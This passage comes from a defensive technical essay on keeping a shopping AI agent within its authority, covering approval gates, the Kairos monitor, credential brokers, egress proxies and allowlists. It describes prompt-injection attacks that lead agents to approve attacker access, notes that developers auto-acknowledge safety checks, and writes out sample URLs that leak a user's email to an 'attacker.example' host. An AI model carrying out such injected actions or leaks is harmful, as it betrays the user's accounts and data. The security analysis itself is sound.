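Under these rules, the instruction "buy one coffee maker for under $50" does not authorize the order. The agent has to request approval again once it has identified the specific coffee maker and the total. CELLMATE requests approval only at the start, so it would need to add a second request to comply.

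OpenAI and Google also run checks on their own servers, but the developer's program reports whether anyone has dealt with them:

| | OpenAI | Google |
|---|---|---|
| What the service sends | A list of pending safety checks, each with an identifier | A safety decision of "require_confirmation", with an explanation |
| What the program sends back | The same identifiers | A field called `safety_acknowledgement`, set to true |
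| When it sends this | With the screenshot taken after the action | With the result of the action |
| Evidence that a person agreed | None | None |

*Class ResponseComputerToolCallOutputItem*, a reference page for one of OpenAI's software libraries, describes these checks as "acknowledged by the developer", which is accurate because the user's answer never reaches OpenAI or Google directly. The program sends the acknowledgement to the service with the result, normally after it has clicked, so the acknowledgement cannot prevent the click.

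OpenAI's service requires a program to acknowledge safety checks before the model can continue. In *Computer tool has unacknowledged safety check*, a 2025 thread on OpenAI's developer forum, a programmer reports that the service rejected a request because a check was still open, and asks how to make the model ignore the problem and continue. A program can easily do this by acknowledging every check automatically, as the starter program does in *Drive a browser with OpenAI Computer Use*, a guide from Steel, a company that provides browsers for agents. Steel tells developers to change this setting for production and have a person approve each check.

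Sample code from Google has a similar flaw. Its function for obtaining confirmation prints the explanation and returns "CONTINUE" without waiting for an answer. Developers are meant to replace this function, but if they forget, the program will appear to request approval while continuing automatically every time. OpenAI's current sample fails closed, so a pending check stops it unless the developer adds a function that asks a person.

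Some of the server's checks are also optional or incomplete. Google lets developers disable certain policies, although the service may still ask for confirmation. Its scan of screenshots for prompt injection is off by default. OpenAI's service can raise a check on a sensitive site, but according to Microsoft's documentation from December 2025, the service checks the current address only if the program provides it.

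For GPT-6 Astra, OpenAI now recommends letting the model write code instead of requesting individual clicks. One script can fill a cart and place an order, so OpenAI tells developers to enforce permissions inside the functions the script calls. Its sample asks a person to approve each script before it runs. This is cautious, but few shoppers could tell from Python code what the script would buy.

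### Kairos: acting first and deciding later

Asking a person to approve every step would make an agent tedious to use, and the evidence that an action is harmful may appear only later. *Kairos*, from October 2026, therefore delays the decision until the last moment before an effect becomes irreversible. Its monitor is for coding agents, but the way it handles outgoing requests applies to browsers too.

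The agent runs in a virtual machine, and the monitor sits outside it, where it sees every file operation and network request. A written policy lists trusted sources, sensitive data and who may receive that data. The monitor releases an effect if the values that steer it, such as a recipient's address, come from a trusted source and the recipient may have the data. It refuses anything that a rule forbids. A second language model or a person decides the remaining cases, which the monitor holds in different ways:

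| Effect | While the decision is open | If the answer is no |
|---|---|---|
| Changing a file | The change goes into a separate layer, and the agent continues | The monitor discards the layer |
| Sending data, for example with a POST request | The request waits at a proxy, and the agent continues with a stand-in reply | The request never leaves |
| Fetching a page with a GET request | The agent waits, because it needs the page | The request never leaves |

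The monitor can discard a file change because it controls both versions of the file, but it can't take back a message sent to an outside party. A second email asking the recipient to ignore the first does not delete it, and a shop that agrees to cancel an order still has the user's name and address. The monitor therefore has to decide whether to allow a request before sending it.

While the monitor holds an effect, the agent may take further steps based on the stand-in reply, so the monitor holds those steps too and settles them all together. If the person refuses, the monitor tells the agent that the effect never happened, because it cannot erase the stand-in reply from the model's context. To buy the coffee maker, the agent needs the shop's real reply, which might contain an order number or report that the card failed. A gate for shopping would therefore work better if it made the agent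 wait.

The main test used AgentDojo, a benchmark with 97 tasks and 629 attempted prompt injections, with GPT-4.1 as both the agent and the second model:

| Defense | Successful attacks | Tasks completed without an attack | Tasks completed under attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 47.0% | 82.7% | 59.8% |
| Progent, a policy on tool calls | 11.5% | 78.2% | 57.6% |
| CaMeL, a plan fixed in advance | 0.2% | 38.0% | 40.7% |
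| Kairos | 2.7% | 85.1% | 69.5% |

When the researchers made the monitor refuse everything it would otherwise have held, the rate of successful attacks hardly changed, but the agent completed only 42.7% of the tasks that contained no attack. Most of the security therefore came from the policy, and holding effects for a later decision kept the agent useful.

On AgentDyn, where the agent must plan its steps as it goes, the share of attacks that succeeded fell from 37.8% to 1.7%. The share of tasks completed under attack also fell, from 55.5% to 37.1%. The loss grew with the number of interruptions. Tasks that continued past one held effect kept 90% of their usefulness, and those that continued past two or more kept 62%. Against an attacker that rewrote its text over six rounds, 8.8% of attacks succeeded, compared with 52.4% without a defense. Most of these successful attacks exploited tasks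 in which the user had told the agent to follow a document, so the second model mistook the document's instructions for the user's.

The overhead was modest. The monitor added about 1.9 milliseconds per file operation and 1.2 milliseconds per network request, while the second model raised token use by 17.7% on harmless tasks and 33.6% under attack. If the second model fails or gives an unreadable answer, the monitor blocks the effect.

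*Kairos* reports no tests with a human approver. In the runs without attacks, the policy released 83% of effects by itself, and the second model allowed all but one of the rest. A person in the second model's place would have had to judge about one effect in six and would almost always have approved it, a pattern that can lead people to stop reading the requests.

The benchmarks also used simulated tools. Each action reached the monitor with a name and labelled arguments, and the policy specified in advance whether the action was reversible. A browser's requests have no such labels, so a similar monitor for shopping would still need something like CELLMATE's map to recognize the request that places an order.

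## Giving the agent separate credentials

A gate that checks requests has to catch a harmful one before it leaves the browser, but a designer can also make the request fail when it arrives. If a shop accepts orders only with a credential, such as a password or a login cookie, and only the gate has that credential, an order that avoids the gate will not go through. Many browsing agents, however, can already use the credential because they work in a browser where the user is logged in.

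### The confused deputy

Norm Hardy's *The Confused Deputy* (1988) tells the "nearly true" story of a compiler at the computing company Tymshare. The compiler had permission to write files in a system directory because it collected statistics there. Users could also name a file for debugging output. One user gave the name of the company's billing file, which was in the same directory, and the compiler overwrote the billing records.

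Hardy calls the compiler a confused deputy because it had authority from two sources, the user and its own license, and no way to tell the operating system which one it was using. Checking file names would not have helped much, because the billing file wasn't the only sensitive one and someone would have had to update the compiler whenever a new sensitive file appeared. Hardy's remedy is a capability, an item that identifies an object and authorizes its use. The user would give the compiler a capability for the output file instead of a name, and a user with no right to the billing file would have no capability for it.

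A logged-in browser has the same problem as the compiler. *Cookies* (2026), a draft standard from the IETF, the body that standardizes internet protocols, attributes the problem to separating URLs from cookies. The URL identifies what is being requested, the cookie authorizes the request, and the browser may attach the cookie even when someone else chose the URL. In the Operator attack, the attacker used a GitHub issue to direct the agent to a Hacker News page, which the agent opened with the user's logged-in session.

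In *The Agent Clicks Approve*, Hossen (2026) tested what a page can do with this authority. In the main scenario, the user asks for a summary of a page about a billing export. A two-sentence note on the page says the export cannot continue until someone clears an access review, and recommends the "default positive option". The review is an outside program's request for access to the user's account, and the agent clicks "Approve access". In a second scenario, the agent registers an attacker's address to receive the account's billing events.

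Without a defense, agents using Claude Haiku 4.5 and GPT-5.5 completed the unauthorized action in all 73 runs. When the note was harmless, no agent attempted the action in 92 runs. When Haiku 4.5 was instructed that only the user's task could authorize an approval, 7 of 10 attacks still succeeded. Each scenario used a single note and both models are now dated, so these rates may not hold for other attacks or newer agents. But one successful attack can do a lot of damage, because the attacker's access continues after the agent's session ends.

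### When a missed route does no harm

Credentials relax what complete mediation demands of the gate. Without them, every possible route must also be a checked route (R ⊆ C). For a protected action such as placing an order, let V be the routes in R on which the request arrives with a credential that the shop accepts for orders. A request on any other route fails, so it is enough that

V ⊆ C

Suppose the gate does not cover service workers, WebSockets and the command line. If the agent's browser holds the user's login cookie, all three may be in V. If only the gate holds the cookie, V contains only the route through the gate, and the condition holds even though the other routes stay open. *Sovereign Execution Broker* applies the same principle to cloud systems.

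This argument relies partly on the shop, which must require the credential on every path. If an old version of the checkout accepts orders without it, that path is back in V. The agent must also have no way to obtain the credential. If it can open the user's webmail, it may be able to reset the shop password and log in by itself.

The argument doesn't work for public pages, because anyone can open them without a credential. It doesn't work for leaks either. Once the agent has read the user's address, it can send the address to an attacker's server, which will accept any request.

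### The arrangements compared

Designers can separate the agent's authority from the user's to very different degrees:

| Arrangement | What a hijacked agent can do | What the user loses | Does an order have to pass the gate? |
|---|---|---|---|
| The user's own profile | Act in every account where the user is logged in | Nothing | No |
| An empty profile | Use public pages and leak what the task contains | Saved logins, addresses and order history | The user has to sign in or pay, which can serve as the check |
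| A separate shop account with $50 | Spend up to $50 on the wrong things and read the delivery address | Time to set it up, and any benefits of the main account | No, but the loss has a limit |
| A short-lived token for one order | Place one order within the token's limits | The choice of shops, since the shop has to support such tokens | Yes, if the gate issues the token only after approval |
| A broker that fills in the password | Anything the account permits after sign-in | A moment to approve each sign-in | No, only the sign-in does |
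| A broker that attaches the login cookie | Whatever the broker's rules permit | Some pages may not work | Yes |

### The user's profile and an empty one

Running the agent in the user's own profile is the most convenient option and the most dangerous. According to Microsoft's *Browse with Copilot*, the agent in the Edge browser cannot access saved passwords, autofill data or the wallet, but it can access cookies, so it is automatically signed in wherever the user is. The Cloud Security Alliance reports that researchers have used such inherited logins to take over a victim's Slack and X accounts through Claude in Chrome. Microsoft suggests starting with a new profile or deleting all cookies before using the agent.

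The Brave browser creates that new profile itself. The company says the profile shares no cookies, logins or caches with the user's regular one. In May 2026 the feature was available in all release channels, but users had to switch it on in the experimental settings. In the coffee maker example, a hijacked agent in this profile could still search the shop and fill a cart, but it would have no account to charge. The user would sign in or enter a card at checkout.

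An empty profile stays empty only if nobody signs in. If the user logs in to pay, the agent has that session too, unless the user takes over for the last step and then closes the profile. Playwright can keep a profile in memory without ever saving it to disk, but it also has an option to load saved login data into that profile at the start.

Running the browser on a remote server doesn't guarantee an empty profile either. *Mind the Web* (2025), a security study of these agents, separates agents in the user's active browser from those in a clean local browser or an isolated remote one. It notes that some remote agents, such as Operator, let the user log in during a session and keep the login information for later sessions. Amazon's cloud division, AWS, sells this as a feature. *Amazon Bedrock AgentCore Browser now supports browser profiles* (2026) describes saved profiles that keep an agent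 logged in between sessions, which cuts setup time from minutes to tens of seconds. This is useful for a company with thousands of sessions a day, but each new session starts with the authority of the last login.

### A separate account with $50 in it

A separate account can exist on the user's computer or at the shop. Windows has experimental support for agent accounts on the computer. In *Securing AI agents on Windows* (2025), Microsoft announced that agents would get their own standard accounts, which have no administrator rights. According to Microsoft's *Experimental Agentic Features* (2025), an agent can request read and write access to six of the user's folders, including Documents and Downloads. In newer preview builds, Windows asks the user for consent by default. The agent can also open any folder that all signed-in users share.

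Browsers on Windows normally store their cookies outside those six folders, so the agent's Windows account should not inherit the user's logins. But the shop cannot tell which Windows account sent a request. It identifies the shop account only by the cookie in the request, so the agent also needs a separate account at the shop.

Suppose the user opens a second account with a prepaid balance of $50, one delivery address, and no saved card, automatic top-up or option to pay later. A hijacked agent can then spend at most $50, however many orders it places. The shop checks each order against the balance on its own server, so an $84 order fails even if the checkout page still shows $42. The limit also holds if the order travels over a WebSocket or the gate's map is out of date, two cases that CELLMATE does not cover.

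The balance enforces only part of the errand's rules. The agent could break the one-order limit by buying two $24 coffee makers separately. It could also spend the whole $50 on a digital gift card for the attacker. If the shop lets the agent change the delivery address or the account's email address, a hijacked agent might also take over the account, although it would gain little more than the balance.

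The user can use the balance as a check by keeping it at zero until the cart is ready. After reviewing the cart, the user loads exactly $42 from another device. Until then, no order can go through by any route, because the money serves as the credential the agent lacks. But the money isn't tied to the cart. A hijacked agent could swap the coffee maker for something else at $42 after the user loads the money, so the gate would still need to compare the final order with the one the user approved.

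### Tokens that expire

A token is a piece of data that a program presents instead of a password. The service that issues it can limit what it permits and how long it lasts. In an example in *Sovereign Execution Broker*, a broker obtains an Amazon cloud credential that permits one kind of change to one group of firewall settings and lasts up to 900 seconds. Someone who steals it can make only that kind of change to those settings, for at most 15 minutes.

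An agent could buy many coffee makers with a fifteen-minute token that permits "orders up to $50", so the token would also need a limit of one use. When Amazon's own rules cannot specify the exact network port that a change may open, the broker checks the port itself before forwarding the request. Similarly, if a shop's tokens can restrict the account but not the price, the gate still has to check the price.

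Few services seem to offer agents such narrow tokens. *The Secrets Agentic AI Leaves Behind* (Winterford, Vakil and colleagues, 2025), a report from the identity company Okta, examined how plugins connect Microsoft's Security Copilot to other companies' security products. It found that 75% of the plugins supported long-lived API keys, 20% supported usernames and passwords, and 5% supported a method that issues short-lived tokens, which can still permit far too much before they expire. The report also assessed several remote servers that offer tools to agents through MCP, and found that an agent had the same access as the user who authorized it.

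### Filling in a password without showing it

If the agent has to sign in to an ordinary shop, a password manager can act as a broker, a trusted program that uses a secret on the agent's behalf. Cohen and Culea (2026), in *1Password for Claude*, announced such a broker in July 2026. As 1Password describes it, a sign-in goes through these steps:

1. Claude asks for a login and names the site.
2. The 1Password desktop app shows the user the request with a matching login. The user can approve it, pick another login or refuse.
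3. Claude stops reading the page.
4. 1Password's browser extension fills in the password, submits the form and checks that the submission happened. If it failed, the extension clears the password from the page.
5. Claude resumes on the page that follows.

The prompt in the desktop app gives the user a trusted path, as long as the agent is confined to the browser. The extension fills a password only into a site that matches the saved login, so a page that imitates the shop at another address doesn't receive it. 1Password assumes that any other extension may try to contact its extension, and it requires cryptographic proof that each request belongs to a registered agent session. Claude's extension did not check the sender this way when LayerX found ClaudeBleed.

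While an agent controls a tab, 1Password hides its usual suggestions on the page so that the agent can't click them. The arrangement runs only on Macs, does not support passkeys, and may not work with buttons such as "Sign in with Google", according to 1Password's setup guide.

Cloud browsers can use a similar broker. *Closing the credential risk gap for AI agents using a browser* (Wang, 2025) describes a version for Browserbase in which the user approves the request on their own device. An encrypted channel then carries the password to 1Password's extension in the remote browser. Chrome's built-in password manager plays a similar role, and the model has no direct access to stored passwords, according to Parker.

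Playwright offers a weaker substitute. The developer puts passwords in a secrets file, and the model types a placeholder that Playwright replaces with the real value. Playwright also removes matching text from what it returns to the model. Playwright's guide calls this "a convenience, not a security boundary". A page could display the password with a space between the letters, and Playwright would not remove it because the text would no longer match. A hijacked agent might also type the placeholder into a form on the attacker's site, unless something else restricts which sites it can visit.

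### The session cookie carries the authority

Keeping the password from the model prevents serious harm. An attacker with the password could log in from any computer until the user changed it, and could try it on other sites. But a hijacked agent that is already signed in doesn't need the password to place an order.

When the user signs in, the browser sends the password to the shop once. The shop checks it and returns a cookie that usually contains a session identifier, a random value the shop uses to look up who logged in. The browser then sends the cookie instead of the password with each request, so an order from a hijacked agent looks the same to the shop whether the user typed the password or 1Password filled it in. 1Password lists this as an accepted risk and relies on the agent maker's safeguards to control what the agent does after sign-in.

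An agent with a command line or debugging tools may also be able to copy the cookie out of the browser, though an agent that only clicks and types cannot normally read it. The IETF warns that encrypting a cookie's contents does not stop an attacker from using the cookie in another browser.

Shops could make the cookie less powerful. The IETF describes sites that issue two cookies, one for reading and one for making changes, and ask the user to log in again if the second is missing. The proposal addresses links from other websites, but it would suit agents too. The agent's browser could hold the reading cookie while the gate holds the one for making changes. Keeping both in the agent's browser would not limit the agent, because requests made from the shop's own pages would carry both.

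### A broker that keeps the cookie

*CapSeal* (Jin, Guo and Cheung, 2026) goes further and never gives the agent a reusable secret, not even a session token. The agent sends its request without the secret to a broker on the same computer. The broker checks the method, host and path, limits the size, rejects any login header the agent has added, and compares the body with a permitted format. It attaches the secret and sends the request only after these checks pass. It also removes credentials from the reply.

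Jin and colleagues designed the broker for API keys and for SSH, a system for controlling remote computers. A version for the coffee maker might work like this:

1. The broker signs in to the shop and keeps the cookie.
2. The agent browses the shop through the broker, which attaches the cookie to requests that view or change the cart.
3. When the agent tries to order, the broker holds the request and shows the user the details.
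4. If the user approves, the broker attaches the cookie and sends the order.

An order that takes any other route reaches the shop without a login, so the shop has no account to charge. Separate credentials also improve on CELLMATE's handling of an incomplete map. If the shop adds a "buy now" button that the map doesn't include, the broker can withhold the cookie, and the order fails. However, harmless parts of the account also stop working until someone adds them to the map. The broker would also have trouble with sites that store login data in the page itself, and it has to decrypt the traffic, so it can read everything the agent does at the shop.

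In tests of *CapSeal*, agents that held an API key directly revealed it in every trial when a prompt tried to extract it, while agents that used the broker never did. The broker added about 0.15 milliseconds per web request. The tests cannot show whether the broker prevents misuse, because no system, including those without a broker, made an unauthorized request that succeeded. Jin and colleagues assume that the attacker has no administrator rights on the computer, since an administrator could read the broker's memory.

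A broker with poor rules is itself a confused deputy. If it attaches the cookie to every request the agent sends, the web page still determines the action and the user's account still authorizes it. The broker has to compare each request with what the user asked for.

Hossen tested such a comparison at the service. Before the agent started, the service received a list of what the task authorized, such as access for one named program to one named account. The agents followed the malicious note in all 70 attack runs. They sent 103 requests, because some tried again after a refusal, and the service rejected them all. It accepted the action in all 73 runs where the task had named it. The lists were correct by design, so the test doesn't measure how well software could derive them from a user's words.

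A broker could make the same comparison if the request contains all the relevant details. Approving access is harder because the service stores the name of the program and the account, and the request may not repeat them. If it doesn't, the service has to do the checking.

In 49 of the 53 runs in which the service refused to grant access, the agent used its final answer to tell the user to approve the request, usually in the attacker's words. A user who follows that advice approves the request with their own login, and it never passes through the agent's broker.

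## Enforcing the rules at the network

A hijacked agent can leak the user's address even if it has separate credentials. To prevent this, the gate has to control which servers the agent can reach. A gate outside the browser's virtual machine can do this even if an attacker has taken over the browser. However, encryption hides most of what the browser sends, so the gate may be able to detect that the agent is connected to the shop but not whether it is placing an order.

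### One request, stage by stage

Suppose the browser opens a new connection and sends an order to `https://www.shop.example/place-order`. The request leaves the virtual machine in four stages:

1. Name lookup. The browser asks a DNS server for the numeric network address of `www.shop.example`.
2. Connection. The browser connects to that address, normally on port 443.
3. Encryption handshake. The browser and the shop agree on keys. The browser's first message normally contains the host name in plain text, because one server may hold many websites and has to pick the right certificate.
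4. HTTP message. The browser sends the method, path, cookies and form contents in encrypted form.

Each stage supports different rules:

| Stage | What the gate can see | A rule it can enforce | What it can miss |
|---|---|---|---|
| Name lookup | Host name | Answer only for the shop and its image host | A program that connects straight to a numeric address |
| Connection | Numeric address and port | Allow only listed addresses on port 443 | Which of several sites at that address the browser wants |
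| Handshake | The host name in the first message | Refuse handshakes for other hosts | A false host name |
| HTTP message, still encrypted | Size and timing | Limit how much data goes out | Whether the message is an order |
| HTTP message, decrypted | Full URL, method, cookies and form contents | Hold the order for approval | Data that a page's script has encrypted separately |

AWS's *Control which domains your AI agents can access* (2026) describes a gate at the third stage for AgentCore Browser, the company's cloud browser for agents. A firewall reads the host name in each handshake and compares it with the customer's allowlist. AWS calls this the first layer of a larger defense, which seems right because the firewall can keep the agent away from a bank but can't enforce the $50 limit or recognize a sign-in page on the shop's own host.

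Browsers also send many requests over each open connection, so a gate that checks only the first three stages may run just once for the whole shopping trip. That is enough to enforce a rule about hosts, but the gate must check every message to enforce a rule about orders.

### A proxy as the only way out

An egress proxy is a server that receives outgoing traffic and can block it. In some setups, only a browser setting sends traffic through the proxy. Playwright has one option that sets the proxy and another that lists domains for which the browser bypasses it. One of Playwright's own examples includes `.com` in that list, which would apparently exempt most shops.

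Other programs often find the proxy through environment variables such as `HTTP_PROXY`. According to Anthropic, most common tools use these variables, but the built-in `fetch()` function in Node.js, a system for running JavaScript outside the browser, ignores them by default. A hijacked agent with a command line can run a program that connects directly. In the notation for complete mediation, the direct connection is in R, the set of possible routes, but not in C, the set of checked routes.

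The remedy is to take the direct connection out of R. Anthropic describes several ways to do this:

- A container has no network access at all, only a local socket that leads to a proxy outside it.
- A virtual machine has no external network interface and reaches the proxy through a private channel to the host computer. Firecracker, software for running small virtual machines, can start one in under 125 milliseconds with less than 5 MiB of extra memory.
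- In a cloud service, the agent runs in a private network without an internet gateway, and a firewall blocks all outgoing traffic except to the proxy.

AWS offers both kinds of arrangement. Its *Customize AI agent browsing with proxies, profiles, and extensions* announced that customers could route the browser's traffic through their own proxy; previously, sessions had connected directly to the internet. The firewall design is stronger because it puts the browser in a private network with no direct route to the internet, and changing a browser setting doesn't create one.

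A tester can check whether a proxy is mandatory by running a program that ignores it and trying to reach an allowed site. The attempt should fail. Anthropic reports that plain `ssh` and most database drivers cannot connect even to allowed hosts from inside the sandbox that Claude Code can put around its shell commands. This is inconvenient but correct behavior for a mandatory proxy.

That sandbox covers only shell commands, though. According to Anthropic, Claude's web-fetching tool, local MCP servers and computer use all run outside it. A browser that Claude operates through a local copy of Playwright MCP would therefore connect directly to the network, whatever the sandbox's allowlist contains. Anthropic advises users who want one boundary around everything to run the whole process in a container, a virtual machine or its separate sandbox program.

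The shell sandbox is also off by default. If a user turns it on but it cannot start, Claude Code runs commands without it, unless another setting is on that makes Claude Code exit instead. A stop gate needs that setting, because otherwise a missing software package removes the gate.

### The allowlist for the coffee maker

If the shop is Amazon, Meng and colleagues provide a starting point. Their example policy covers amazon.com and allows four further entries. Judging by their names and the needs of the errand, a stricter list might treat them like this:

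| Host | Likely purpose | Allow it? |
|---|---|---|
| `www.amazon.com` | Products, cart and checkout | Yes |
| `m.media-amazon.com` | Pictures and other fixed files | Yes |
| `images-na.ssl-images-amazon.com` | More pictures | Only if pages need it |
| `*.amazon-adsystem.com` | Advertising | No |
| `*.amazon.dev` | Unclear | Only if something breaks |

When the agent opens a product page, the gate allows the page and its pictures. If the gate blocked the image host, the pictures would be missing, which would handicap an agent that works from screenshots. If a review contains a picture on the attacker's server, the gate refuses the connection before the browser can send the URL. It also refuses any connection to a bank.

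The two entries with asterisks cover every subdomain, including ones nobody has looked at. Omitting them may leave blank spaces where advertisements would appear, but the errand does not need the advertisements. Each entry should also specify port 443, because in Anthropic's sandbox, for example, an entry without a port allows every port on that host.

The list may need hosts unrelated to shopping. If the harness runs inside the virtual machine, it has to reach the servers of the company that runs the model. Similarly, the firewall around GitHub's Copilot agent always allows some hosts that Copilot uses to interact with GitHub. Moving the harness outside the virtual machine keeps the browser's list shorter.

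OpenAI's *Agent internet access* warns that finding the right domains may take some trial and error. For Codex, its coding agent, OpenAI offers a preset of 71 domains, including github.com and google.com. The preset is convenient for programmers but far too broad for an errand at one shop.

### False and hidden host names

The program that opens a connection writes the host name in the handshake, so a program under the attacker's control can connect to the attacker's IP address and write `www.shop.example`. A firewall that checks only the name lets the connection through, and a DNS filter doesn't stop it because the program never looked up a name. A proxy prevents this by looking up the name and opening the connection itself, so a request for the shop can go only to the shop's address.

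Another trick, domain fronting, can still work despite this remedy. Large hosting companies serve many sites from the same machines. A program asks the proxy for an allowed site on such a service, then names the attacker's site inside the encrypted message. If the hosting company routes the message by the second name, the data reaches the attacker. Anthropic and the container software company Docker warn about this in their agent sandboxes. An agent that only clicks and types can't normally do this, because the browser fills in both names, but an agent with a command line can.

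Encrypted Client Hello, a newer addition to the handshake, creates the opposite problem. It encrypts the real host name and shows only the hosting company's. A gate with an allowlist would refuse the connection, which is safe but could make a permitted shop unreachable. An administrator can turn the feature off in the agent's browser, but then other people on the network can see which shop the agent visits. A proxy that the browser knows about avoids most of this problem, because the browser has to give it a host name before the handshake begins.

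### Decrypting traffic at the proxy

An outside gate has to read the HTTP message to enforce the order rule. A proxy can do this by standing in for the shop. It gives the browser its own certificate for `www.shop.example`, decrypts and checks the request, and sends it to the real shop over a second encrypted connection. The browser normally rejects this certificate unless someone installs the proxy's certificate authority, which vouches for it, in the sandbox.

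AWS's *Control where your AI agents can browse with Chrome enterprise policies* (2026) announced support for custom certificate authorities in AgentCore Browser, so agents could open companies' internal sites. The same feature should also let a proxy decrypt traffic.

Decryption allows much narrower rules. The *Agentic Workflow Firewall*, from GitHub's research group GitHub Next, can restrict an agent to particular paths on a site if it decrypts the traffic. OpenAI lets Codex users limit requests to GET, HEAD and OPTIONS, the methods that normally fetch data without changing it. A shopping agent could hardly work under that limit, because adding an item to a cart usually takes a POST request. But with a map like CELLMATE's, a decrypting proxy could allow changes to the cart and hold the order.

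Limiting which HTTP methods an agent can use doesn't prevent it from leaking data through the URL of a GET request. Websites commonly log these URLs, as OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) points out.

Decryption also has serious costs:

- The proxy can read passwords, cookies and card numbers, so it joins the trusted computing base.
- Anyone who steals the certificate authority's key can impersonate any website to the agent's browser. The user should therefore install the certificate only in the sandbox.
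- The browser no longer receives the shop's real certificate, so the proxy has to check it.
- Some programs accept only one particular certificate and stop working.

A system can also decrypt traffic without checking it. Claude Code has an experimental option that decrypts traffic to replace placeholders with real credentials, and Anthropic notes that this option adds no content filtering.

### Traffic that the proxy does not carry

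An ordinary web proxy can't carry some browser traffic. HTTP/3, the newest version of HTTP, and WebRTC, which browsers use for video calls, normally send data over UDP, a simpler alternative to the usual TCP connections. If the sandbox lets UDP out, that traffic bypasses the proxy. Anthropic's shell sandbox lets only TCP traffic out, and Docker's agent sandboxes also block raw TCP connections. Blocking UDP has little effect on the coffee-maker errand, because shops generally support older versions of HTTP too, but a video chat with customer service might fail.

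Name lookups are harder to control because the browser makes them before it connects. If a hijacked agent opens `https://alice-mail-example.attacker.example`, the lookup alone sends Alice's email address, slightly altered, to the attacker's name server. Refusing the connection afterwards does not undo the leak. A DNS name can have up to 253 characters, so an email address fits easily into one lookup, and longer text takes a few more.

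To prevent this, the gate has to check a name before anything looks it up. Anthropic's proxy does the lookup only after the name has passed the allowlist, and a container without a network can't do lookups by itself. AWS's *Network architecture* describes a DNS firewall that can either block lookups for unlisted names or only log them. Logging is useful while someone is working out the list, but the data still gets out until they switch to blocking.

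The gate should also check which addresses a name resolves to. An allowed name might resolve to an address on the user's own computer, where other programs may accept commands without a password. Anthropic's proxy refuses names that resolve only to such local addresses. To allow an exception, the user has to list the numeric address.

### Redirects and sites that fetch pages

A mandatory proxy handles ordinary redirects well. If the shop's forwarding address sends the browser to an attacker's site, the browser has to open a new connection, and the proxy refuses it. Browser Use's watchdog would detect the redirect only after the attacker's server had received the request.

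Checking only the first address is much weaker. The marketing company Stan Ventures reports that OpenAI considered a list of well-known sites for its agents but found gaps, because many legitimate sites redirect visitors elsewhere. OpenAI also worried that frequent warnings would teach people to ignore them. It chose to let agents automatically load only URLs that had already appeared on the public web, much like Chrome's check on addresses that the model writes. A network gate needs the full URL to apply such a rule, so it must decrypt the traffic.

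Checking where the agent connects cannot catch a leak through a permitted site that contacts the attacker. Suppose the shop fetches every picture linked in a review to make a thumbnail. A hijacked agent posts a review with a picture address that points to the attacker's server and contains the user's email. The shop's server requests the picture and so sends the email to the attacker, although the agent's browser has contacted only the shop. To prevent this, the gate would have to decrypt the review and refuse outside links, or the agent would have to lose its permission to post.

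### Someone else's account at an allowed site

An allowlist identifies servers, but a server can hold data for millions of people, including the attacker. Suppose the attacker has an account at the shop and posts the account's password in a product review. A hijacked agent could sign in to that account and save the user's address as the name of a wish list. The attacker would then read the address from another computer. Every connection goes to an allowed host, so a gate that checks only host names would not block the theft.

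The problem is worse at sites made for sharing. Anthropic and Docker both use github.com as an example of a domain too broad to allow lightly. Anyone can open an account there and receive files. A wildcard that covers all of a hosting company's customers creates the same weakness, since the attacker can become a customer.

To close this channel, the rule has to name a pair, the host and the account, rather than the host alone. The gate would need to do several things:

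1. Decrypt the traffic, since cookies and login headers are inside the HTTP message.
2. Recognize whose account each cookie or header belongs to. This is difficult because a session cookie usually looks like random text.
3. Refuse sign-ins to other accounts, including new registrations.
4. Control actions that publish or share data from the user's own account, such as reviews and messages.

A broker that removes any login data the agent supplies and attaches the user's cookie would handle the second step and much of the third. Microsoft and Google also let a company's proxy add a header that lists the organizations whose accounts may sign in, and they reject all others. Consumer shops have little reason to offer this. Even if they did, a hijacked agent could publish the address in a review from the user's own account, so the fourth step remains necessary.

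Removing live access avoids most of these problems. OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode* describes an optional setting that limits ChatGPT's browsing to cached pages, so the agent does not contact the live site. The setting also disables agent mode and, on personal accounts, shopping agents, so it can't be used for the coffee-maker errand. OpenAI warns that some risk remains, for instance through connected apps. After an incident involving Hugging Face, a platform for sharing AI models, OpenAI paused runs in its own research clusters of frontier models that could execute code or use tools with internet access, then reviewed the workloads one by one.

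### Where to intercept the traffic

Meng and colleagues considered three places for CELLMATE to intercept requests:

| Position | Advantage | Drawback |
|---|---|---|
| Outside the browser, in a firewall or proxy | The browser cannot override a refusal | Rules are usually coarse and may affect other programs |
| In the browser's own code | The strongest mediation, according to Meng and colleagues | Someone has to maintain a modified browser, or the browser's maker has to cooperate |
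| In an extension or through Chrome's debugging interface | Easy to install, with a detailed view of browser activity | No other privileged extension or component may interfere |

They chose an extension because people can install it today. Their objection that outside rules affect other programs is much weaker if the agent has its own virtual machine, since all the traffic then belongs to the agent. Their preference for the browser's code fits an agent confined to web pages, but an agent with a command line can send requests without the browser, and only an outside gate would catch those.

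A firewall and an extension work well together. The firewall can restrict the agent to the shop and its image host, while the extension recognizes the order. If another extension interferes with CELLMATE, the agent might get an order past the price limit, but it still couldn't contact the attacker's server directly.

Speed is unlikely to be the deciding factor, since CELLMATE's extension and the monitor in *Kairos*, which runs outside a virtual machine, both added only small delays.

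### Connection Allowlists

Connection Allowlists, which let a website limit the connections of its own pages, are no longer only a trial. Google's *Chrome 152* (2026) lists the feature in the stable release of August 25, 2026. A shop can send this header with a page:

`Connection-Allowlist: (response-origin "https://images.shop.example/*")`

The page may then connect only to the shop's own origin and its image host. According to Google's *Connection Allowlists origin trial* (2026), the list also covers WebRTC and early name lookups. A compromised shop script can't send a customer's card number directly to an unlisted server. The header would also block the preview of a picture hosted on the attacker's server.

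However, the list applies to only one page and does not carry over when the agent opens another. West warns in the draft specification *Connection Allowlists* that a script may get around the list through another page on the same site with looser rules. A service worker also has its own list, so a request that the page cannot make might still go out through the worker.

The header also doesn't stop the agent from navigating to other sites. The Chromium code review *Enforce network restrictions on navigations* suggests that the check applies only to navigations that a page starts. A hijacked agent on the shop's page could then enter `https://attacker.example/?email=alice@mail.example` in the address bar, and the browser would send the request. The page that loaded would be subject only to the attacker's own list, if there was one.

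## Making the gate small enough to verify

To verify a stop gate under Anderson's third requirement, people have to analyze its whole trusted computing base, not only the gate's own code.

### What has to be trusted in each position

The gate's position determines how much other code can break its rules. For the rule that holds the coffee-maker order for approval, the list looks like this:

| Position | What can break the order rule, besides the gate's own code |
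|---|---|
| Browser extension | The browser, the operating system, other extensions that can change requests, and the map that identifies the order |
| The browser's main process | The rest of that process, the operating system and the map |
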